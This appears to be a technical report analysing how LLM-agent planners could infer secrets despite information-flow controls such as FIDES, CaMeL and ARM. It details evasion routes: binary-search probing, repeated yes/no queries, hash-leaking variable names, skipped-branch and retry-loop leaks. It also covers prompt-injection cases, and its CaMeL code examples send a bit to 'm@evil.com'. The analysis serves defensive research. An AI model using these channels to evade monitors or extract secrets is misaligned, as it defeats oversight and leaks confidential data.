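Withholding the explanation protects a rule only if the planner cannot infer it from the replies alone. Several experiments measure how well models make such inferences, but in all of them the model is asked to find the rule and every query gets an accurate answer. In *DiscoverPhysics* (2026), for example, an agent gets a fixed number of experiments to discover the force law of a simulated world. *Active Causal Discovery Benchmark* (2026) compares agents that receive data with agents that can also intervene. None of the experiments described here put the rule behind an information-flow system, so they measure inference skill, not how fast a restricted planner can extract a secret.

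The most careful comparison of chosen and unchosen data comes from Geng, Arumugam and colleagues (2025), in *Are Large Language Models Reliable AI Scientists?*. They built three kinds of black box, a system whose workings the model cannot see:

- 100 short programs that transform lists of numbers
- 46 formal languages, each a rule for which strings of letters are allowed
- an equation from economics for how much a shopper values a basket of goods

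The last two give very short replies. A language box reports only whether it could have produced a given string, and the equation box only which of two baskets is worth more, or that they are equal. Both have about as few possible outcomes as the purchasing tool.

When GPT-4o received random examples, its descriptions of the rule stopped improving after about 10 of them. A Bayesian algorithm, which keeps a probability for each candidate rule and updates it with every example, kept improving up to 100. When GPT-4o was instead given 10 examples and allowed to choose up to 50 queries of its own, its scores rose with the number of queries in all three domains. In one case the rule was some number of As, the same number of Bs, and twice as many Cs. GPT-4o first assumed that the numbers of As and Bs could differ, but it corrected the rule after it submitted strings with unequal numbers and the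 box rejected them.

The improvement could come from better data or from the act of choosing it. To separate the two, Geng and colleagues gave GPT-4o the queries and answers from its own earlier investigations as ready-made examples. In all three domains, it did worse with these examples than when it had made the queries itself. Llama 3.3 also gained little from GPT-4o's records and more from its own queries. Part of the benefit therefore came from forming a guess and testing it. Consistent with this, GPT-4o's score on the formal languages rose from 24.1 to 34.7 when it analyzed the results so far before choosing more queries. Choosing queries did not help on a fourth kind of black box, a board game with unknown winning conditions, perhaps because each query required the model to set up a position, propose a move and predict the result.

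These models date from 2024 and early 2025, so their scores are weak evidence of what current models cannot do. The positive result is more likely to hold for current models, since even GPT-4o could learn a rule from replies of "yes" and "no". The tasks were also much harder than finding an approval limit. A formal language can follow almost any pattern, but the limit is one number in a known range, and a model can find it by repeatedly halving the range, a standard method that it can look up or write as code. A second planner would lose little by working from the first one's record, because the largest accepted order and the smallest refused one contain everything the search has found.

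*AdaExploreBench* (Wang, Lai and colleagues, 2026) tested newer models on a related problem. An agent handles a series of cases, in finance or healthcare for example, and chooses one of four actions for each. A hidden rule determines the best action from some of the case's facts. Before each batch, the agent may invent cases and see how all four actions would score. Partway through, the rule changes without notice. On a scale where random choice gets 0 and perfect choice gets 100, the best of the eight models scored as follows.

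| Model | Score | Average number of distinct probes |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 67.3 | 88 |
| GPT-6 Sol | 61.9 | 99 |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 52.9 | 113 |

When Wang and colleagues forced the agents to probe before every batch, the average number of probes across all models rose from 34 to 54, but the average score fell by 2 points. When they let the agents keep a record of the cases they had already handled, scores rose by 9.4 points on average. They conclude that the agents reason well from good evidence but choose uninformative probes, although they did not measure the quality of the probes directly. The gain from keeping records is weak support for this, because any agent should do better with additional evidence. The drop in score after forced probing is stronger support, and it also suggests that a company cannot judge what a planner has learned by counting its calls.

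The agents were often right about what they did learn. When asked which facts mattered to the rule, Gemini 3.8 Flash named only 67% of them, but 95% of the facts it named were correct. A planner can therefore know part of a secret reliably before it can state all of it.

The unannounced change hurt every model that had learned much of the original rule. Scores fell by 26.9 points on average in the first batch afterward, and in the last two batches these models were still 7 to 19 points below their earlier level. In 36% of the episodes that Wang and colleagues could compare, the agent described the rule the same way before and after the change. The earlier arithmetic on redrawing the approval limit at random assumed a planner that knows when the limit changes, but these results suggest that a planner that doesn't know may keep relying on an old answer. It would be unwise to count on this,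 because the tests did not include the largest current models, such as GPT-6 Astra, and a planner can check an old limit with just two orders, one at the limit and one just above it.

### Learning undocumented tools by trial and error

Agents also probe tools for ordinary reasons, since many tools are poorly documented. Hallinan, Venkatesh and colleagues (2026), in *OpaqueToolsBench*, studied how much of the missing documentation a model can reconstruct. In their method, ToolObserver, the agent first attempts the actual task. A second model then reads the record of calls, results and errors and rewrites the tools' descriptions, and the agent tries again. Earlier systems such as DRAFT (2024) instead made up practice queries for each tool in isolation.

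In one test, the functions' names were disguised and all information about their inputs was removed, leaving only a general description. GPT-5 at first completed none of the tasks because it kept calling the functions without any inputs. After fewer than three rounds of rewriting on average, it completed 86%, compared with 95% when it had the true documentation. In a harder version without the descriptions, it completed 80%, compared with 44% for an earlier method that tests each tool separately.

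ToolObserver worked much less well when the feedback was indirect. In a chess test, GPT-5 had to choose at each turn among three unlabeled tools that suggest moves, one much stronger than the others. It always chose the strongest when given true documentation, and 25% of the time without it. ToolObserver raised this only to 29%, although the agent's results against opponents improved somewhat more. A likely reason is that the outcome of a game depends on dozens of moves, so it is weak evidence about any one tool, whereas an error message arrives immediately and concerns a single call. For a designer who wants to keep information hidden, the reply to each call is therefore a greater risk than later consequences that mix the effects of many calls.

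ToolObserver also saves its rewritten tool descriptions, and later runs read them when several tasks share the same tools. If a previous run has added "orders above 700 fail" to the purchasing tool's description, a planner that starts with an empty conversation can continue the earlier search for the approval limit. An information-flow system would have to label that description as secret, even though it looks like public documentation and no one copied the limit into it, because the model inferred the note from a series of refusals, which is an implicit flow.

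A company could instead discourage trial calls altogether, but its agents may then complete fewer tasks. *Toolcompass* (2026) compares two ways of training agents and tests them on applications they did not meet in training. Agents trained with MatchTIR made far fewer tool calls and rarely ran out of turns, but they completed fewer tasks than agents trained with GRPO, a common method that rewards only the final outcome. With an unfamiliar tool, some of the calls that look wasteful are how the agent finds out what the tool does. A quota strict enough to protect the approval limit would also prevent this learning, unless the planner could practice elsewhere, for instance in a simulated world that contains no real secrets.

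## FIDES, which tracks data but not decisions

FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System) is an agent design that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft to stop prompt injection. It combines labels, policy checks and hidden variables. The variables are hidden to protect the planner from hostile text, and the planner can reveal them at any time. A company with a secret approval limit might well start with FIDES, but this hiding would not stop the planner from reading the limit.

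### Labels and checks

A conversation normally starts as public and trusted, because the software gives that label to the user's request and the developer's instructions. Tools then label what they return. Most results have some structure, so a tool can label a whole list of emails or individual fields, such as each email's sender, subject and body. When the planner reads a result, the conversation takes on any stricter label, and so does every call the planner requests afterward.

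Before a tool call runs, the software compares the call's labels with the policy for that tool. Costa and colleagues describe two basic policies. Under the first, a consequential call such as a payment goes ahead only if both its arguments and the decision to make it are trusted. Under the second, information may go out only if every recipient is allowed to read it. The comparison uses only labels, so the wording of an email cannot change the outcome. If the call runs, its result gets the combined label of the call, its arguments and everything in storage that the tool may have read.

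In the tests of FIDES, the tools for sending emails and chat messages had to satisfy only one of the two policies, and the trust policy covered only the decision to call a tool. A planner in a trusted conversation could therefore send confidential text to anyone. Assuming that the user wanted this is reasonable if the only worry is a hijacked planner, but it means fully trusting a planner that nobody has hijacked. Costa and colleagues also do not check sending the conversation to the model or replying to the user, although they note that a designer could.

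### Hidden variables and limited answers

FIDES hides a piece of data only if reading it would raise the conversation's label. It first compares the label of the whole result with the conversation's. If the result's label is stricter, FIDES stores the entire result in a new variable and shows the planner the variable's name. If not, it applies the same test to each part of the list or record, until every part is either visible or in a variable. The conversation keeps its old label throughout.

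The planner has not read the variable's contents, so its decision to pass the variable to another tool is still trusted, even if the contents are not. For example, a policy can require a message's recipient to come from trusted data but let the text come from a web search.

FIDES gives the planner two tools for finding out what a variable contains. One puts the contents into the conversation, which then takes on their label. The other sends the contents to the quarantined model with a question and stores the answer in a new variable. The planner can specify the type of answer: yes or no, one item from a fixed list, or free text. The software can enforce this choice by preventing the quarantined model from generating anything else.

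The answer's type becomes part of its label. FIDES ranks types by how much information they can carry, from yes/no at the bottom to free text at the top, and a policy can make exceptions for types that carry little. In one example, a user asks the agent to create a calendar event if any of three emails requests a meeting. The planner gets a yes/no answer from the quarantined model and opens it. If the answer is yes, the planner has the quarantined model extract the details into another variable and passes that variable to the calendar. The opened answer came from untrusted emails, so the conversation is now untrusted. But a policy may allow the calendar call, because an attacker could have influenced the planner by at most one bit.

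Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 office, banking, travel and chat tasks in which attackers plant instructions in the data. With GPT-4o as the planner, attacks succeeded 152 times against an ordinary agent and never against FIDES with its checks switched on. The results are good evidence that the checks stop injection, but they provide little evidence about whether FIDES can keep secrets from the planner, because the software put only untrusted data into variables. The planner could read secret data, and the checks only limited where it could send that data afterward. The tests also did not enforce answer types, which most tasks did not need.

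### Explicit secrecy

The secrecy guarantee for FIDES is about the tools' storage, which has public and secret parts. Let d₁ be the contents of the storage when a run starts, σ the state of the agent's software, including the conversation so far, and m the latest message. As the run proceeds, its steps change the storage, and g is the function that describes those changes. Write d₁ =_L d₂ if d₁ and d₂ have the same public contents. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every d₁,

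whenever (σ, m, d₁) →*_g (σ′, m′, d₁′), then g(d₁) =_L g(d₂) for every d₂ with d₁ =_L d₂.

If the steps the agent actually took are rerun on storage that differs only in its secrets, the public contents must come out the same.

Suppose an agent posts "large" on a public page if the approval limit is above 500 and posts nothing otherwise. When the limit is 700, it posts "large". Repeating that same step with a stored limit of 300 would still post "large", so the agent satisfies explicit secrecy. Noninterference instead compares the original run with what the agent does when the limit is 300. The agent then posts nothing, so it violates noninterference.

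Costa and colleagues are open about this gap. They write that an adversary who sees the sequence of tool calls may be able to infer limited information from the agent's decisions, and they place timing and the length of network packets outside their model. (NeuroTaint, a later system that has its own comparison with FIDES, also records influence on decisions.)

The formula covers even less than their description suggests, although they do not mention this. It holds the conversation and the arguments of every call fixed. If the planner reads the limit and types "700" into a public message, the steps of that run write "700" whatever limit the storage contains, so the condition is satisfied. The software is stricter here than the guarantee. FIDES would still block the message under its second policy, because the conversation is secret by then.

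### Whether noninterference is too strict

Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy because they consider noninterference too restrictive for agents. Under noninterference, an agent that had called any tool that may read a secret could no longer call any tool that may write to a public place. For example, an assistant that had read one confidential email could not update a public web page for the rest of the run. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracking system for Android phones, also accept a weaker guarantee than noninterference.

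This argument is convincing for the paper's adversary, who watches every change to public storage but never sees the conversation. It is weaker if the planner is the observer. Noninterference then requires that everything returned to the planner be the same for all values of the secret. If this holds, the planner's later decisions cannot depend on the secret, so there is no need to forbid public calls after a secret one. The labels only have to keep secret values out of anything the planner can read later.

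Noninterference toward the planner would not forbid most useful calls, but it would seriously limit the planner on tasks in which the right next step depends on the secret. Costa and colleagues' classification of AgentDojo gives a rough idea of how common these tasks are. They call a task data-dependent if no single sequence of calls and final reply solves it for all possible data. That applies to 5% of the office tasks, 10% of the travel tasks, and just over 40% of both the banking and the chat tasks, or about a fifth of the whole benchmark. A planner that learned nothing from its tools could in principle complete the rest by passing variables along and letting the quarantined model interpret them. However, it would also be unable to repair calls that fail because of a secret, which the classification doesn't measure.

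FIDES does not keep secrets from the planner, most obviously because the planner can open any variable. Opening one restricts where the information may go next, but by then the planner has read it. To prevent this, a designer could remove the tool that opens variables, or use the optional check on messages to the model to block any conversation that contains secret data.

### What a hidden result still reveals

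A planner that cannot open variables still learns something from a hidden result. Costa and colleagues don't list what remains visible, but one can infer much of it from their hiding procedure and naming rules.

The planner always sees that the call returned. It also sees the variable's name, which in the paper's tests contained the tool's name, a running number and, where relevant, the list position and field name. If the tool labels the whole result secret, the planner sees nothing else. But if only inner fields have the stricter label, the software opens the list or record around them, and the planner can count the items and read the field names and any fields that are not hidden. The procedure has no separate rule for errors, because in the paper's model a tool always returns a result. Whether an error message ends up in a variable therefore depends on how a developer builds the system.

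In one published test run, the planner used the number of hidden items to choose the right action without reading any hidden text. The user asked the agent to add Alice to the chat channel with the fewest messages. The software had hidden the channels' names and all the messages, and this version of the agent could neither open variables nor use a quarantined model. The planner requested each channel's messages and received lists of variable names. One list was empty, so it added Alice to that channel.

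Visible fields can also reveal hidden ones. In a banking task, the planner had to find the price of a New Year's gift, but the software had hidden the transaction descriptions. Only one transaction was dated January 1, so the planner reported its amount. Costa and colleagues count this as guesswork that makes the benchmark scores less reliable. The same guess would also leak information if a company wanted to keep the descriptions secret.

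How much structure the planner sees depends on how developers apply labels. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, which covers moving the method into real products, describes a convention for the Model Context Protocol in which a list without its own label takes on the labels of its contents. Under the FIDES procedure, one secret item would then hide the entire list, including its length. But Microsoft also expects agents to be more capable with finer labels, which would put only the sensitive parts in variables and leave the structure visible. The planner could then count the items again.

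Variable names may also leak hidden data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up to the FIDES paper, shows a web page whose untrusted parts have been replaced by names such as VAR_2_d41d8cd9. Two of the names end in d41d8cd9, and both stand for empty text. The MD5 hash of empty text starts with the same eight characters. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from data, so the names seem to contain fingerprints of the hidden text. This does no harm in the paper's example, which is a public forum page. But if a variable hid the approval limit, a planner able to run code could compute the fingerprints of all 1,024 possible limits and look for the match without probing.

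### Yes/no questions that the planner can repeat

A policy that lets the planner read yes/no answers creates another channel. Suppose a variable contains the approval limit and the planner asks the quarantined model whether the number is above 512. The answer reveals one bit, as intended. But the planner can keep halving the range, as it could with orders, and learn the limit after ten answers. Unlike the orders, these questions produce no purchases or refusals for anyone to notice.

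FIDES cannot detect this from its labels. When it combines two labels, it keeps the larger of the two types, so combining two yes/no labels gives another yes/no label. A conversation with ten yes/no answers therefore has the same label as a conversation with one. This rule can track whether any secret data is present, since adding more secret data doesn't change that, but it cannot measure the total amount of information, which adds up across answers.

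Fixed lists are riskier because the planner writes them. If it lists all 1,024 possible limits, it needs only one question to find the right one. A policy that accepts fixed lists would have to restrict their length as well as the number of questions.

The one-bit argument is stronger when the threat is prompt injection. An outside attacker who controls the text can influence the answer, but the planner chooses the question and is not colluding with the attacker.

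A designer could count the bits the planner receives about each secret and refuse further questions after, say, three. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests related research into labels that record how much information each output carries about its labeled inputs. To limit what repeated questions leak, the system would have to add up these amounts over the whole conversation, and over later ones if the planner can remember earlier answers.

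### Planning around the checks

Costa and colleagues' planner had no access to the policies and often attempted actions they blocked. Kolluri and colleagues built PRUDENTIA, an agent that extends FIDES. It shows the planner the labels and policies, requires it to write down a reason before opening a variable, and lets it ask the user to endorse untrusted data. Endorsement saves effort when one document leads to many actions. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can approve the email once instead of approving each task.

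The evaluation measured how many AgentDojo tasks the agent completed without any human approval, and the total number of approvals it needed for the tasks it completed when approvals were unlimited.

| Planner model | Agent | Tasks completed without approval | Approvals over all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | FIDES | 50% | 8 |
| GPT-4o | PRUDENTIA | 43% | 24 |
| GPT-5 | FIDES | 57% | 41 |
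| GPT-5 | PRUDENTIA | 73% | 7 |

The additional instructions made the older model worse and the newer one much better. Current models are stronger than GPT-5, so they probably benefit too.

These gains are for agents that defend against injection, and some of the changes would be harmful if information had to be kept from the planner. When PRUDENTIA's planner opens a variable without endorsement, the software also opens all the others. Kolluri and colleagues reason that the conversation is already untrusted at that point, so hiding the rest no longer saves any approvals. If the variables held secrets, a request to see one value would disclose every hidden value.

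PRUDENTIA also has a small channel that bypasses variables. If the quarantined model cannot answer a question, it replies with the fixed sentence "I need more information/variables." The software treats this sentence as trusted and shows it directly to the planner, which can therefore tell whether a question was answered without opening a variable. The planner could learn whether the hidden number is above 512 by telling the quarantined model to give that reply if it is, although nobody has reported testing this.

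Kolluri and colleagues considered letting the user declassify data (lower its secrecy label) in the same way as endorsing it. They decided against it because whether private information may be shared depends heavily on the situation, and approving individual calls accounts for that better. But that approval happens when data is about to leave the system, which is too late if the planner itself should not have seen the data.

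### FIDES in Microsoft's products

Microsoft released FIDES in May 2026 as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its library for building agents. Automatic hiding is on by default, but it covers only untrusted data. In the main example in Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), an attacker's instructions lead the agent to read a file of passwords, which the tool labels private and trusted. Because the file is labeled trusted, its contents go straight into the planner's conversation. The conversation is now private, so the software blocks the agent from posting a public comment.

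The secrecy label is also easy to forget. The release post and the later documentation from Microsoft differ on whether unlabeled results count as trusted, but both treat them as public. The documentation describes its default of "untrusted" as the safe choice, which is true for injection, but the default of "public" is the permissive choice for secrecy.

Microsoft and GitHub have also added experimental FIDES support to GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. The agent keeps one label for the conversation and enforces policies for selected tools. GitHub's server labels data from private repositories as private and trusted, so Agent Framework's automatic hiding would leave that data visible too.

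The versions of FIDES respond differently to a forbidden call. The paper's algorithm ends the run. In the experiments, the software reported the block to the planner, which could then try something else. Agent Framework stops the tool and returns an error by default, but a developer can configure it to require a person's approval instead. It also has a dry-run setting that blocks nothing.

A planner normally learns about labels from a block, not about the data, but labels can be informative. In Costa and colleagues' tests, only an email's sender and recipients were allowed to read it. If the software had hidden those names, a planner could have tried sending the email to one colleague after another and used the blocks to work out who had sent or received it. This would work only where the policy requires authorized readers even in a trusted conversation, and each successful attempt would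 send the email.

Microsoft's sample policy for chat channels looks up the channel's current members and lists, in its approval request, those who are not allowed to read the message. A human reviewer needs this explanation, but the planner should not receive it if the membership or the list of allowed readers is secret. Repeated attempts would not necessarily indicate bad intent, since Kolluri and colleagues found that in most unsuccessful runs the agent kept requesting actions that the checks had already rejected.

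None of these checks would stop the planner from searching for the approval limit, because each order contains only a public number that the planner chose. If a developer extended hiding to secrets, and the purchasing tool returned receipts and refusals in the same form, the planner would see only a variable name after each order. But if refusals came back as visible errors, or a policy let the planner read a yes/no answer to "was the order accepted?", the planner could find the limit in 10 orders.

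## CaMeL, where a skipped branch and a retry loop leak

The planner in FIDES sees at least the outline of each tool's result before it chooses the next call. In CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues designed in 2025, the planner writes the whole plan as a program before any tool runs, and ordinary software then executes it. If the program finishes on the first attempt, the planner sees no tool output. But Garby and colleagues found two leaks in CaMeL, one in how it labels variables and one in the code that restarts a failed program.

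### Planning before reading

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes how CaMeL divides the work between two models and an interpreter. The privileged model, the planner, turns the user's request into a program, which can call the quarantined model to read untrusted data. The interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from, and checks the security policy before every tool call.

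Each value's label lists which sources influenced the value and who may read it. In Garby and colleagues' simplified version of CaMeL's banking policy, a payment goes through only if the recipient's account number is trusted and the recipient may read the amount, subject and date.

They also rebuilt an attack from the CaMeL paper. Alice asks her agent to send a reminder about a meeting with Bob, but an attacker has added a postscript to Bob's last email asking for a cancellation. An ordinary agent read the email and sent the cancellation. A planner that wrote its program before anything opened the email had already fixed the subject and text, so the reminder went out as Alice intended. The program still took Bob's address from the email, with the quarantined model's help, so an attacker could have changed the address. Only a policy check on that value would catch the change.

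Planning first seems to provide most of CaMeL's protection on benchmarks. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's chat tasks with four recent models, with its policy checks on and off. It resisted every attack in both settings. Depending on the model, it completed 13 to 17 of the 21 tasks with the checks off, but only 4 to 6 with them on. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* says CaMeL's task performance is comparable to that of undefended agents, which fits these results only when the checks are off.

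The checks matter more when the plan lets data determine which tools are called. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. Garby and colleagues found two runs, both with the checks off, in which the planner wrote a program that matched each instruction in the file to a tool. Whoever edited the file could then choose the tool calls, even though the planner never read the file.

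### A tool call under a secret condition

CaMeL handles the simplest implicit flow correctly. In an example from Garby and colleagues, an attacker wants to know whether a customer's balance is above some threshold:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The message is a constant, so its own label is public. But the interpreter also keeps a program-counter label. The test reads the balance, so that label becomes secret inside this conditional, and the interpreter blocks the email. Explicit secrecy, the guarantee behind FIDES, does not cover this kind of flow.

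The refusal still depends on the balance. If the balance is low, the program skips the email and finishes, but if it is high, the policy stops the program. Anyone who can see whether the run finished therefore learns whether the balance was low or high. Termination-insensitive noninterference permits this leak.

### How a skipped assignment keeps its public label

A program can get the email past the check by recording the answer in variables first:

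```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When CaMeL's interpreter changes a variable inside a conditional, it adds the program-counter label to that variable. When it skips the conditional, it leaves the variable's label as it was. The two possible runs then look like this:

| Step | Low balance | High balance |
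|---|---|---|
| Start | `tmp` and `rich` are True, public | `tmp` and `rich` are True, public |
| Test of the balance | Skipped, so `tmp` stays True, public | `tmp` becomes False, secret |
| Test of `tmp` | `rich` becomes False, public | Skipped, so `rich` stays True, public |
| Test of `rich` | No email | The interpreter sends the email |

The labeling first goes wrong in the low-balance run, where `tmp` is still True only because the balance is low. Its value depends on a secret but its label is public, so the interpreter also treats the change to `rich` as public. In the high-balance run, `tmp` has the correct label, but the program skips the only assignment that would have passed that label to `rich`. In both runs `rich` ends up public, and its value shows whether the balance is above the threshold.

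`tmp` alone would leak something, because the program could send an email whenever `tmp` was still True. The second variable gives the program a copy of the answer that is public whatever the balance is. The program can store this copy, calculate with it or put it in a message, and it can repeat the trick for one threshold after another in a single run that finishes normally. Buiras, Stefan and Russo (2014), in *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, warn that labels that change during a run can open a high-bandwidth covert channel like this one if a run-time monitor handles them naively.

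How much this matters depends on who writes the program. An outside attacker does not write CaMeL's programs, so under prompt injection the leak would mostly happen by accident, though it could happen easily. Suppose a plan sets a status to "fine", changes it to "low" if the balance is under $100, and emails the status to an accountant who isn't allowed to see the balance. If the balance is low, the policy blocks the email. Otherwise the email goes out, and the accountant learns that the balance is at least $100. A planner could also write such code on purpose to extract a secret, and CaMeL trusts the planner's program.

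### Why watching one run is not enough

Garby and colleagues trace the example to a 1974 paper by Fenton, which Denning later rewrote in conventional code. Fenton's abstract computer, the Data Mark Machine, blocks any assignment that would move secret information into a public variable. According to Denning, Fenton proved that this machine can safely ignore skipped assignments as long as no variable's label changes.

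Fixed labels stop the program above from leaking the balance through `rich`. If `tmp` is permanently public, the machine blocks any attempt to set it to False under a secret condition, so `tmp` is True whatever the balance. If `tmp` is permanently secret, testing it makes the program-counter label secret in both runs, and the machine then blocks any change to a public `rich`. Either way, `rich` has the same value in both runs.

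In CaMeL a variable's label changes with its contents, so Fenton's proof does not apply. The same variable can be public in one run and secret in another, depending on the secret, but a run-time monitor observes only one run. Russo and Sabelfeld argue in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis* that a purely run-time monitor with changing labels must either miss some leaks or stop some harmless programs that an analysis of the code in advance would accept.

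An analysis done before the plan runs covers both branches, so it would detect that `tmp` might change under a secret condition and label it secret from then on, whichever branch runs. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) similarly recommends a purpose-built language for plans that would let a checker verify a plan's information flows before it runs. CaMeL's current language resembles Python, which is hard to analyze this way, partly because Python programs rely heavily on exceptions, errors that interrupt the normal order of execution. Any line after a call that might raise an exception runs only if the call succeeded, so the call acts as a condition on the rest of the program even though the code contains no "if".

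CaMeL also has no proof that its labeling is correct. Garby and colleagues point out that its Python code is in effect the only definition of its rules, which makes the rules hard to audit. They also found a more basic mistake in the code, where inserting an untrusted value into text made the value trusted. This is an explicit flow, which taint tracking is supposed to catch. Their own agent language, LLMbda, has a machine-checked proof.

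### Stopping the run at a risky assignment

To prevent the untaken-branch leak, LLMbda uses a rule from *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis* (Austin and Flanagan, 2009), a paper on tracking information in languages like JavaScript without analyzing programs in advance. The rule stops the run whenever code under a secret condition is about to change a public variable. In the example above, a run with a high balance stops at `tmp = False`, while a run with a low balance continues and sets `rich` to False. Neither run sends an email, and the only thing that depends on the balance is whether the run finishes.

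The rule also stops some harmless programs. *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (Austin and Flanagan, 2009) gives the example of a program that sets a public variable to true, changes it to false if a secret is true, then sets it back to true and returns it. The result is always true, so it reveals nothing, but the rule stops the program whenever the secret is true. Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues note that the rule stops a program even if it never uses the changed variable again.

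To stop fewer programs, Austin and Flanagan proposed letting the assignment go ahead but marking the variable as "partially leaked". The program stops only if it later uses the marked variable in a sensitive way, for example in a condition. The three treatments compare as follows when the secret condition is true:

| When a secret condition changes a public variable | Leaking program | Harmless program |
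|---|---|---|
| Relabel the variable and continue | Finishes and leaks | Finishes |
| Stop at once | Stops at `tmp = False` | Stops |
| Mark the variable and continue | Stops at the test of `tmp` | Finishes |

A program can avoid the later stop by declaring the variable secret just before testing it, so that its label is the same in every run. Austin and Flanagan also showed how to add these declarations automatically. They suggest first releasing a version of a web application that never stops but records where declarations are needed, then enforcing the rule only once the list has settled. This spreads the work over many users of one program, but it suits agents less well because a planner writes a new program for each task, which may never have a second user. The first run could also leak, because the trial version gives no guarantee.

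The simpler option is to tell the planner to declare such variables secret from the start. A cooperative planner would probably learn to do this, and its programs would stop less often. With an uncooperative planner, the rule still prevents the silent leak, but the planner can choose when to make a program stop. It then matters whether the planner finds out that the program stopped.

### The retry loop outside the monitor

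Programs written by a model often contain mistakes, so CaMeL runs its interpreter inside a retry loop. After a failure, the loop sends the planner information about the error, and the planner writes another program. Garby and colleagues found that this loop is ordinary Python code outside the interpreter, so nothing in it has a label. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, as with the refused email, but the loop handles that result as if it were public. The next attempt also starts with clean labels, even though the planner wrote it after learning about the earlier errors.

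Each attempt can therefore leak the one bit that termination-insensitive noninterference tolerates, and the planner can choose each program based on the earlier outcomes, as it could when restarting the purchasing tool after a crash. The series of outcomes can identify the secret even if every program satisfies the guarantee.

The amount that leaks depends on what the planner can tell about a failure. Suppose a retry loop allows ten attempts and normally ends when a program succeeds. If all failures look the same to the planner, it can observe only which attempt succeeded, if any, which distinguishes 11 cases. But if the planner can tell a policy block from an ordinary error, it can write a program that attempts a forbidden email if the secret is above some number and otherwise divides by zero. The program always fails, so the loop always continues, and the kind of failure reveals whether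 the secret is above that number. Ten attempts then distinguish 2^10, or 1,024, cases.

To reduce this leak, CaMeL censors error messages between attempts, but Garby and colleagues report that it gives no formal guarantee for the censoring. Censoring is still worthwhile because it can prevent a message from quoting a secret outright, and if it made every failure look identical, it would limit the planner to the 11 cases above. It cannot hide that an attempt failed, because each failure triggers a request for another program. The ten-attempt limit applies only within one task, so a planner that remembers earlier results can continue during the next one. Thorough censoring also makes some failures harder to repair.

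Restarting may also repeat an action, because a program that the policy stops halfway may already have sent a message or made a payment.

The obvious fix is to track the retry loop as well. The outcome of a failed attempt would then be treated as secret, and so would every program the planner wrote after seeing it. But the policy would block most of the publicly visible actions in such a program, so one failure could keep the planner from finishing the task. LLMbda avoids this by letting the planner test programs in a simulated world before its single real run.

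Zhou and colleagues also insist that retry logic belongs inside the system that enforces the policy. Their agent framework, ELBA, has models write programs in Haskell, whose compiler checks in advance that each operation receives the right type of data and has only permitted effects. If a program fails this check, ELBA returns the compiler's error to the model for correction. It does not retry after runtime errors. The check happens before the program calls any tools, so the compiler's error cannot depend on what those calls would have returned.

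This restriction did not seem to hurt performance much. ELBA needed about 0.1 retries per request to the model, and only 7 of 2,688 runs ran out of retries. With policies enforced, it completed 8 to 10 of the 21 chat tasks, compared with CaMeL's 4 to 6. Some of this advantage comes from letting models read data and then write further programs, so ELBA as a whole does not keep tool results from the planner. Its retry rule could still be useful in a system that does keep them from the planner. The rule would be harder to apply to CaMeL's Python-like programs, because many of their errors appear only when the program runs.

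Suppose CaMeL labels the purchasing tool's replies as secret. A single program could place ten orders, use skipped assignments to copy each reply into a public variable, use that copy to choose the next amount, and write the approval limit somewhere the planner will read it later. Austin and Flanagan's rule would stop this program. But the planner could still find the limit in ten attempts by placing one order in each, provided it could tell a policy stop from an error it had caused on purpose.

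## ARM and NeuroTaint, which record influence as well as data

CaMeL's retry loop reports a program's failure to the planner, but no label records what information the planner may have gained from it. Two designs from April 2026 are meant to record this influence. ARM, the Agentic Reference Monitor, records refused calls and blocks later calls that may depend on them. NeuroTaint examines an agent's log after the run and estimates which inputs led to which actions.

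### Denial feedback

When a security check blocks a call, the tool never runs, so ordinary taint tracking has no returned data to label. But the planner receives the refusal. Suppose a request for one employee's disciplinary file returns "access denied", while a request for a made-up employee's file returns "no such file". The different responses reveal that the first file exists, even though the planner has read neither.

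Chinaei, who designed ARM, calls one use of this feedback causality laundering. It has four parts:

- The agent attempts a protected action, and the system refuses it.
- The agent infers something from the refusal.
- The agent passes on what it inferred through a later call that looks harmless.
- No returned data connects the two calls, so a tracker that follows only data finds nothing wrong.

Chinaei addresses prompt injection, where an outside attacker directs these steps and gains nothing until the agent makes the later call. A company that wants to keep information from the planner is harmed as soon as the agent makes the inference. Chinaei also cites evidence that agents can infer hidden monitoring from blocked actions alone.

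*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives a machine-checked proof that refusals can leak a secret. In the example, a user has a secret setting of 0 or 1, and only setting 1 lets the agent use an internal logging tool. An attacker's email makes the model call this tool. The attacker cannot see the log, so the call reveals nothing as long as refusals stay hidden. If the attacker can see which tool the system refused, for example in an error message, they learn the setting. The same reasoning applies to a planner that sees its own refusals, but the framework leaves out models that use the monitor's replies to decide when to follow an injected instruction, so it is of little use for analyzing adaptive probing.

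A refusal can also be harmless. In another of Dongol's examples, a quarantined model writes a reply using private notes, and the monitor blocks the reply because its label is private. The monitor blocks it whatever the notes contain, so an observer who sees only the name of the refused tool learns nothing about them. An observer who also sees the refused message can learn about the notes, because the model may have quoted them. A refusal therefore reveals a secret only if the decision to refuse depended on the secret, or if the error message repeats text that depended on it.

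### How ARM links a refusal to the next call

ARM sits between the agent and its tools and checks every call in four stages, any of which can block the call. It first applies fixed rules, such as a ban on reading password files and a maximum of 100 calls to any one tool per session. It then checks where the call's inputs came from, applies limits based on the tool's input description, and finally applies rules written by the operator.

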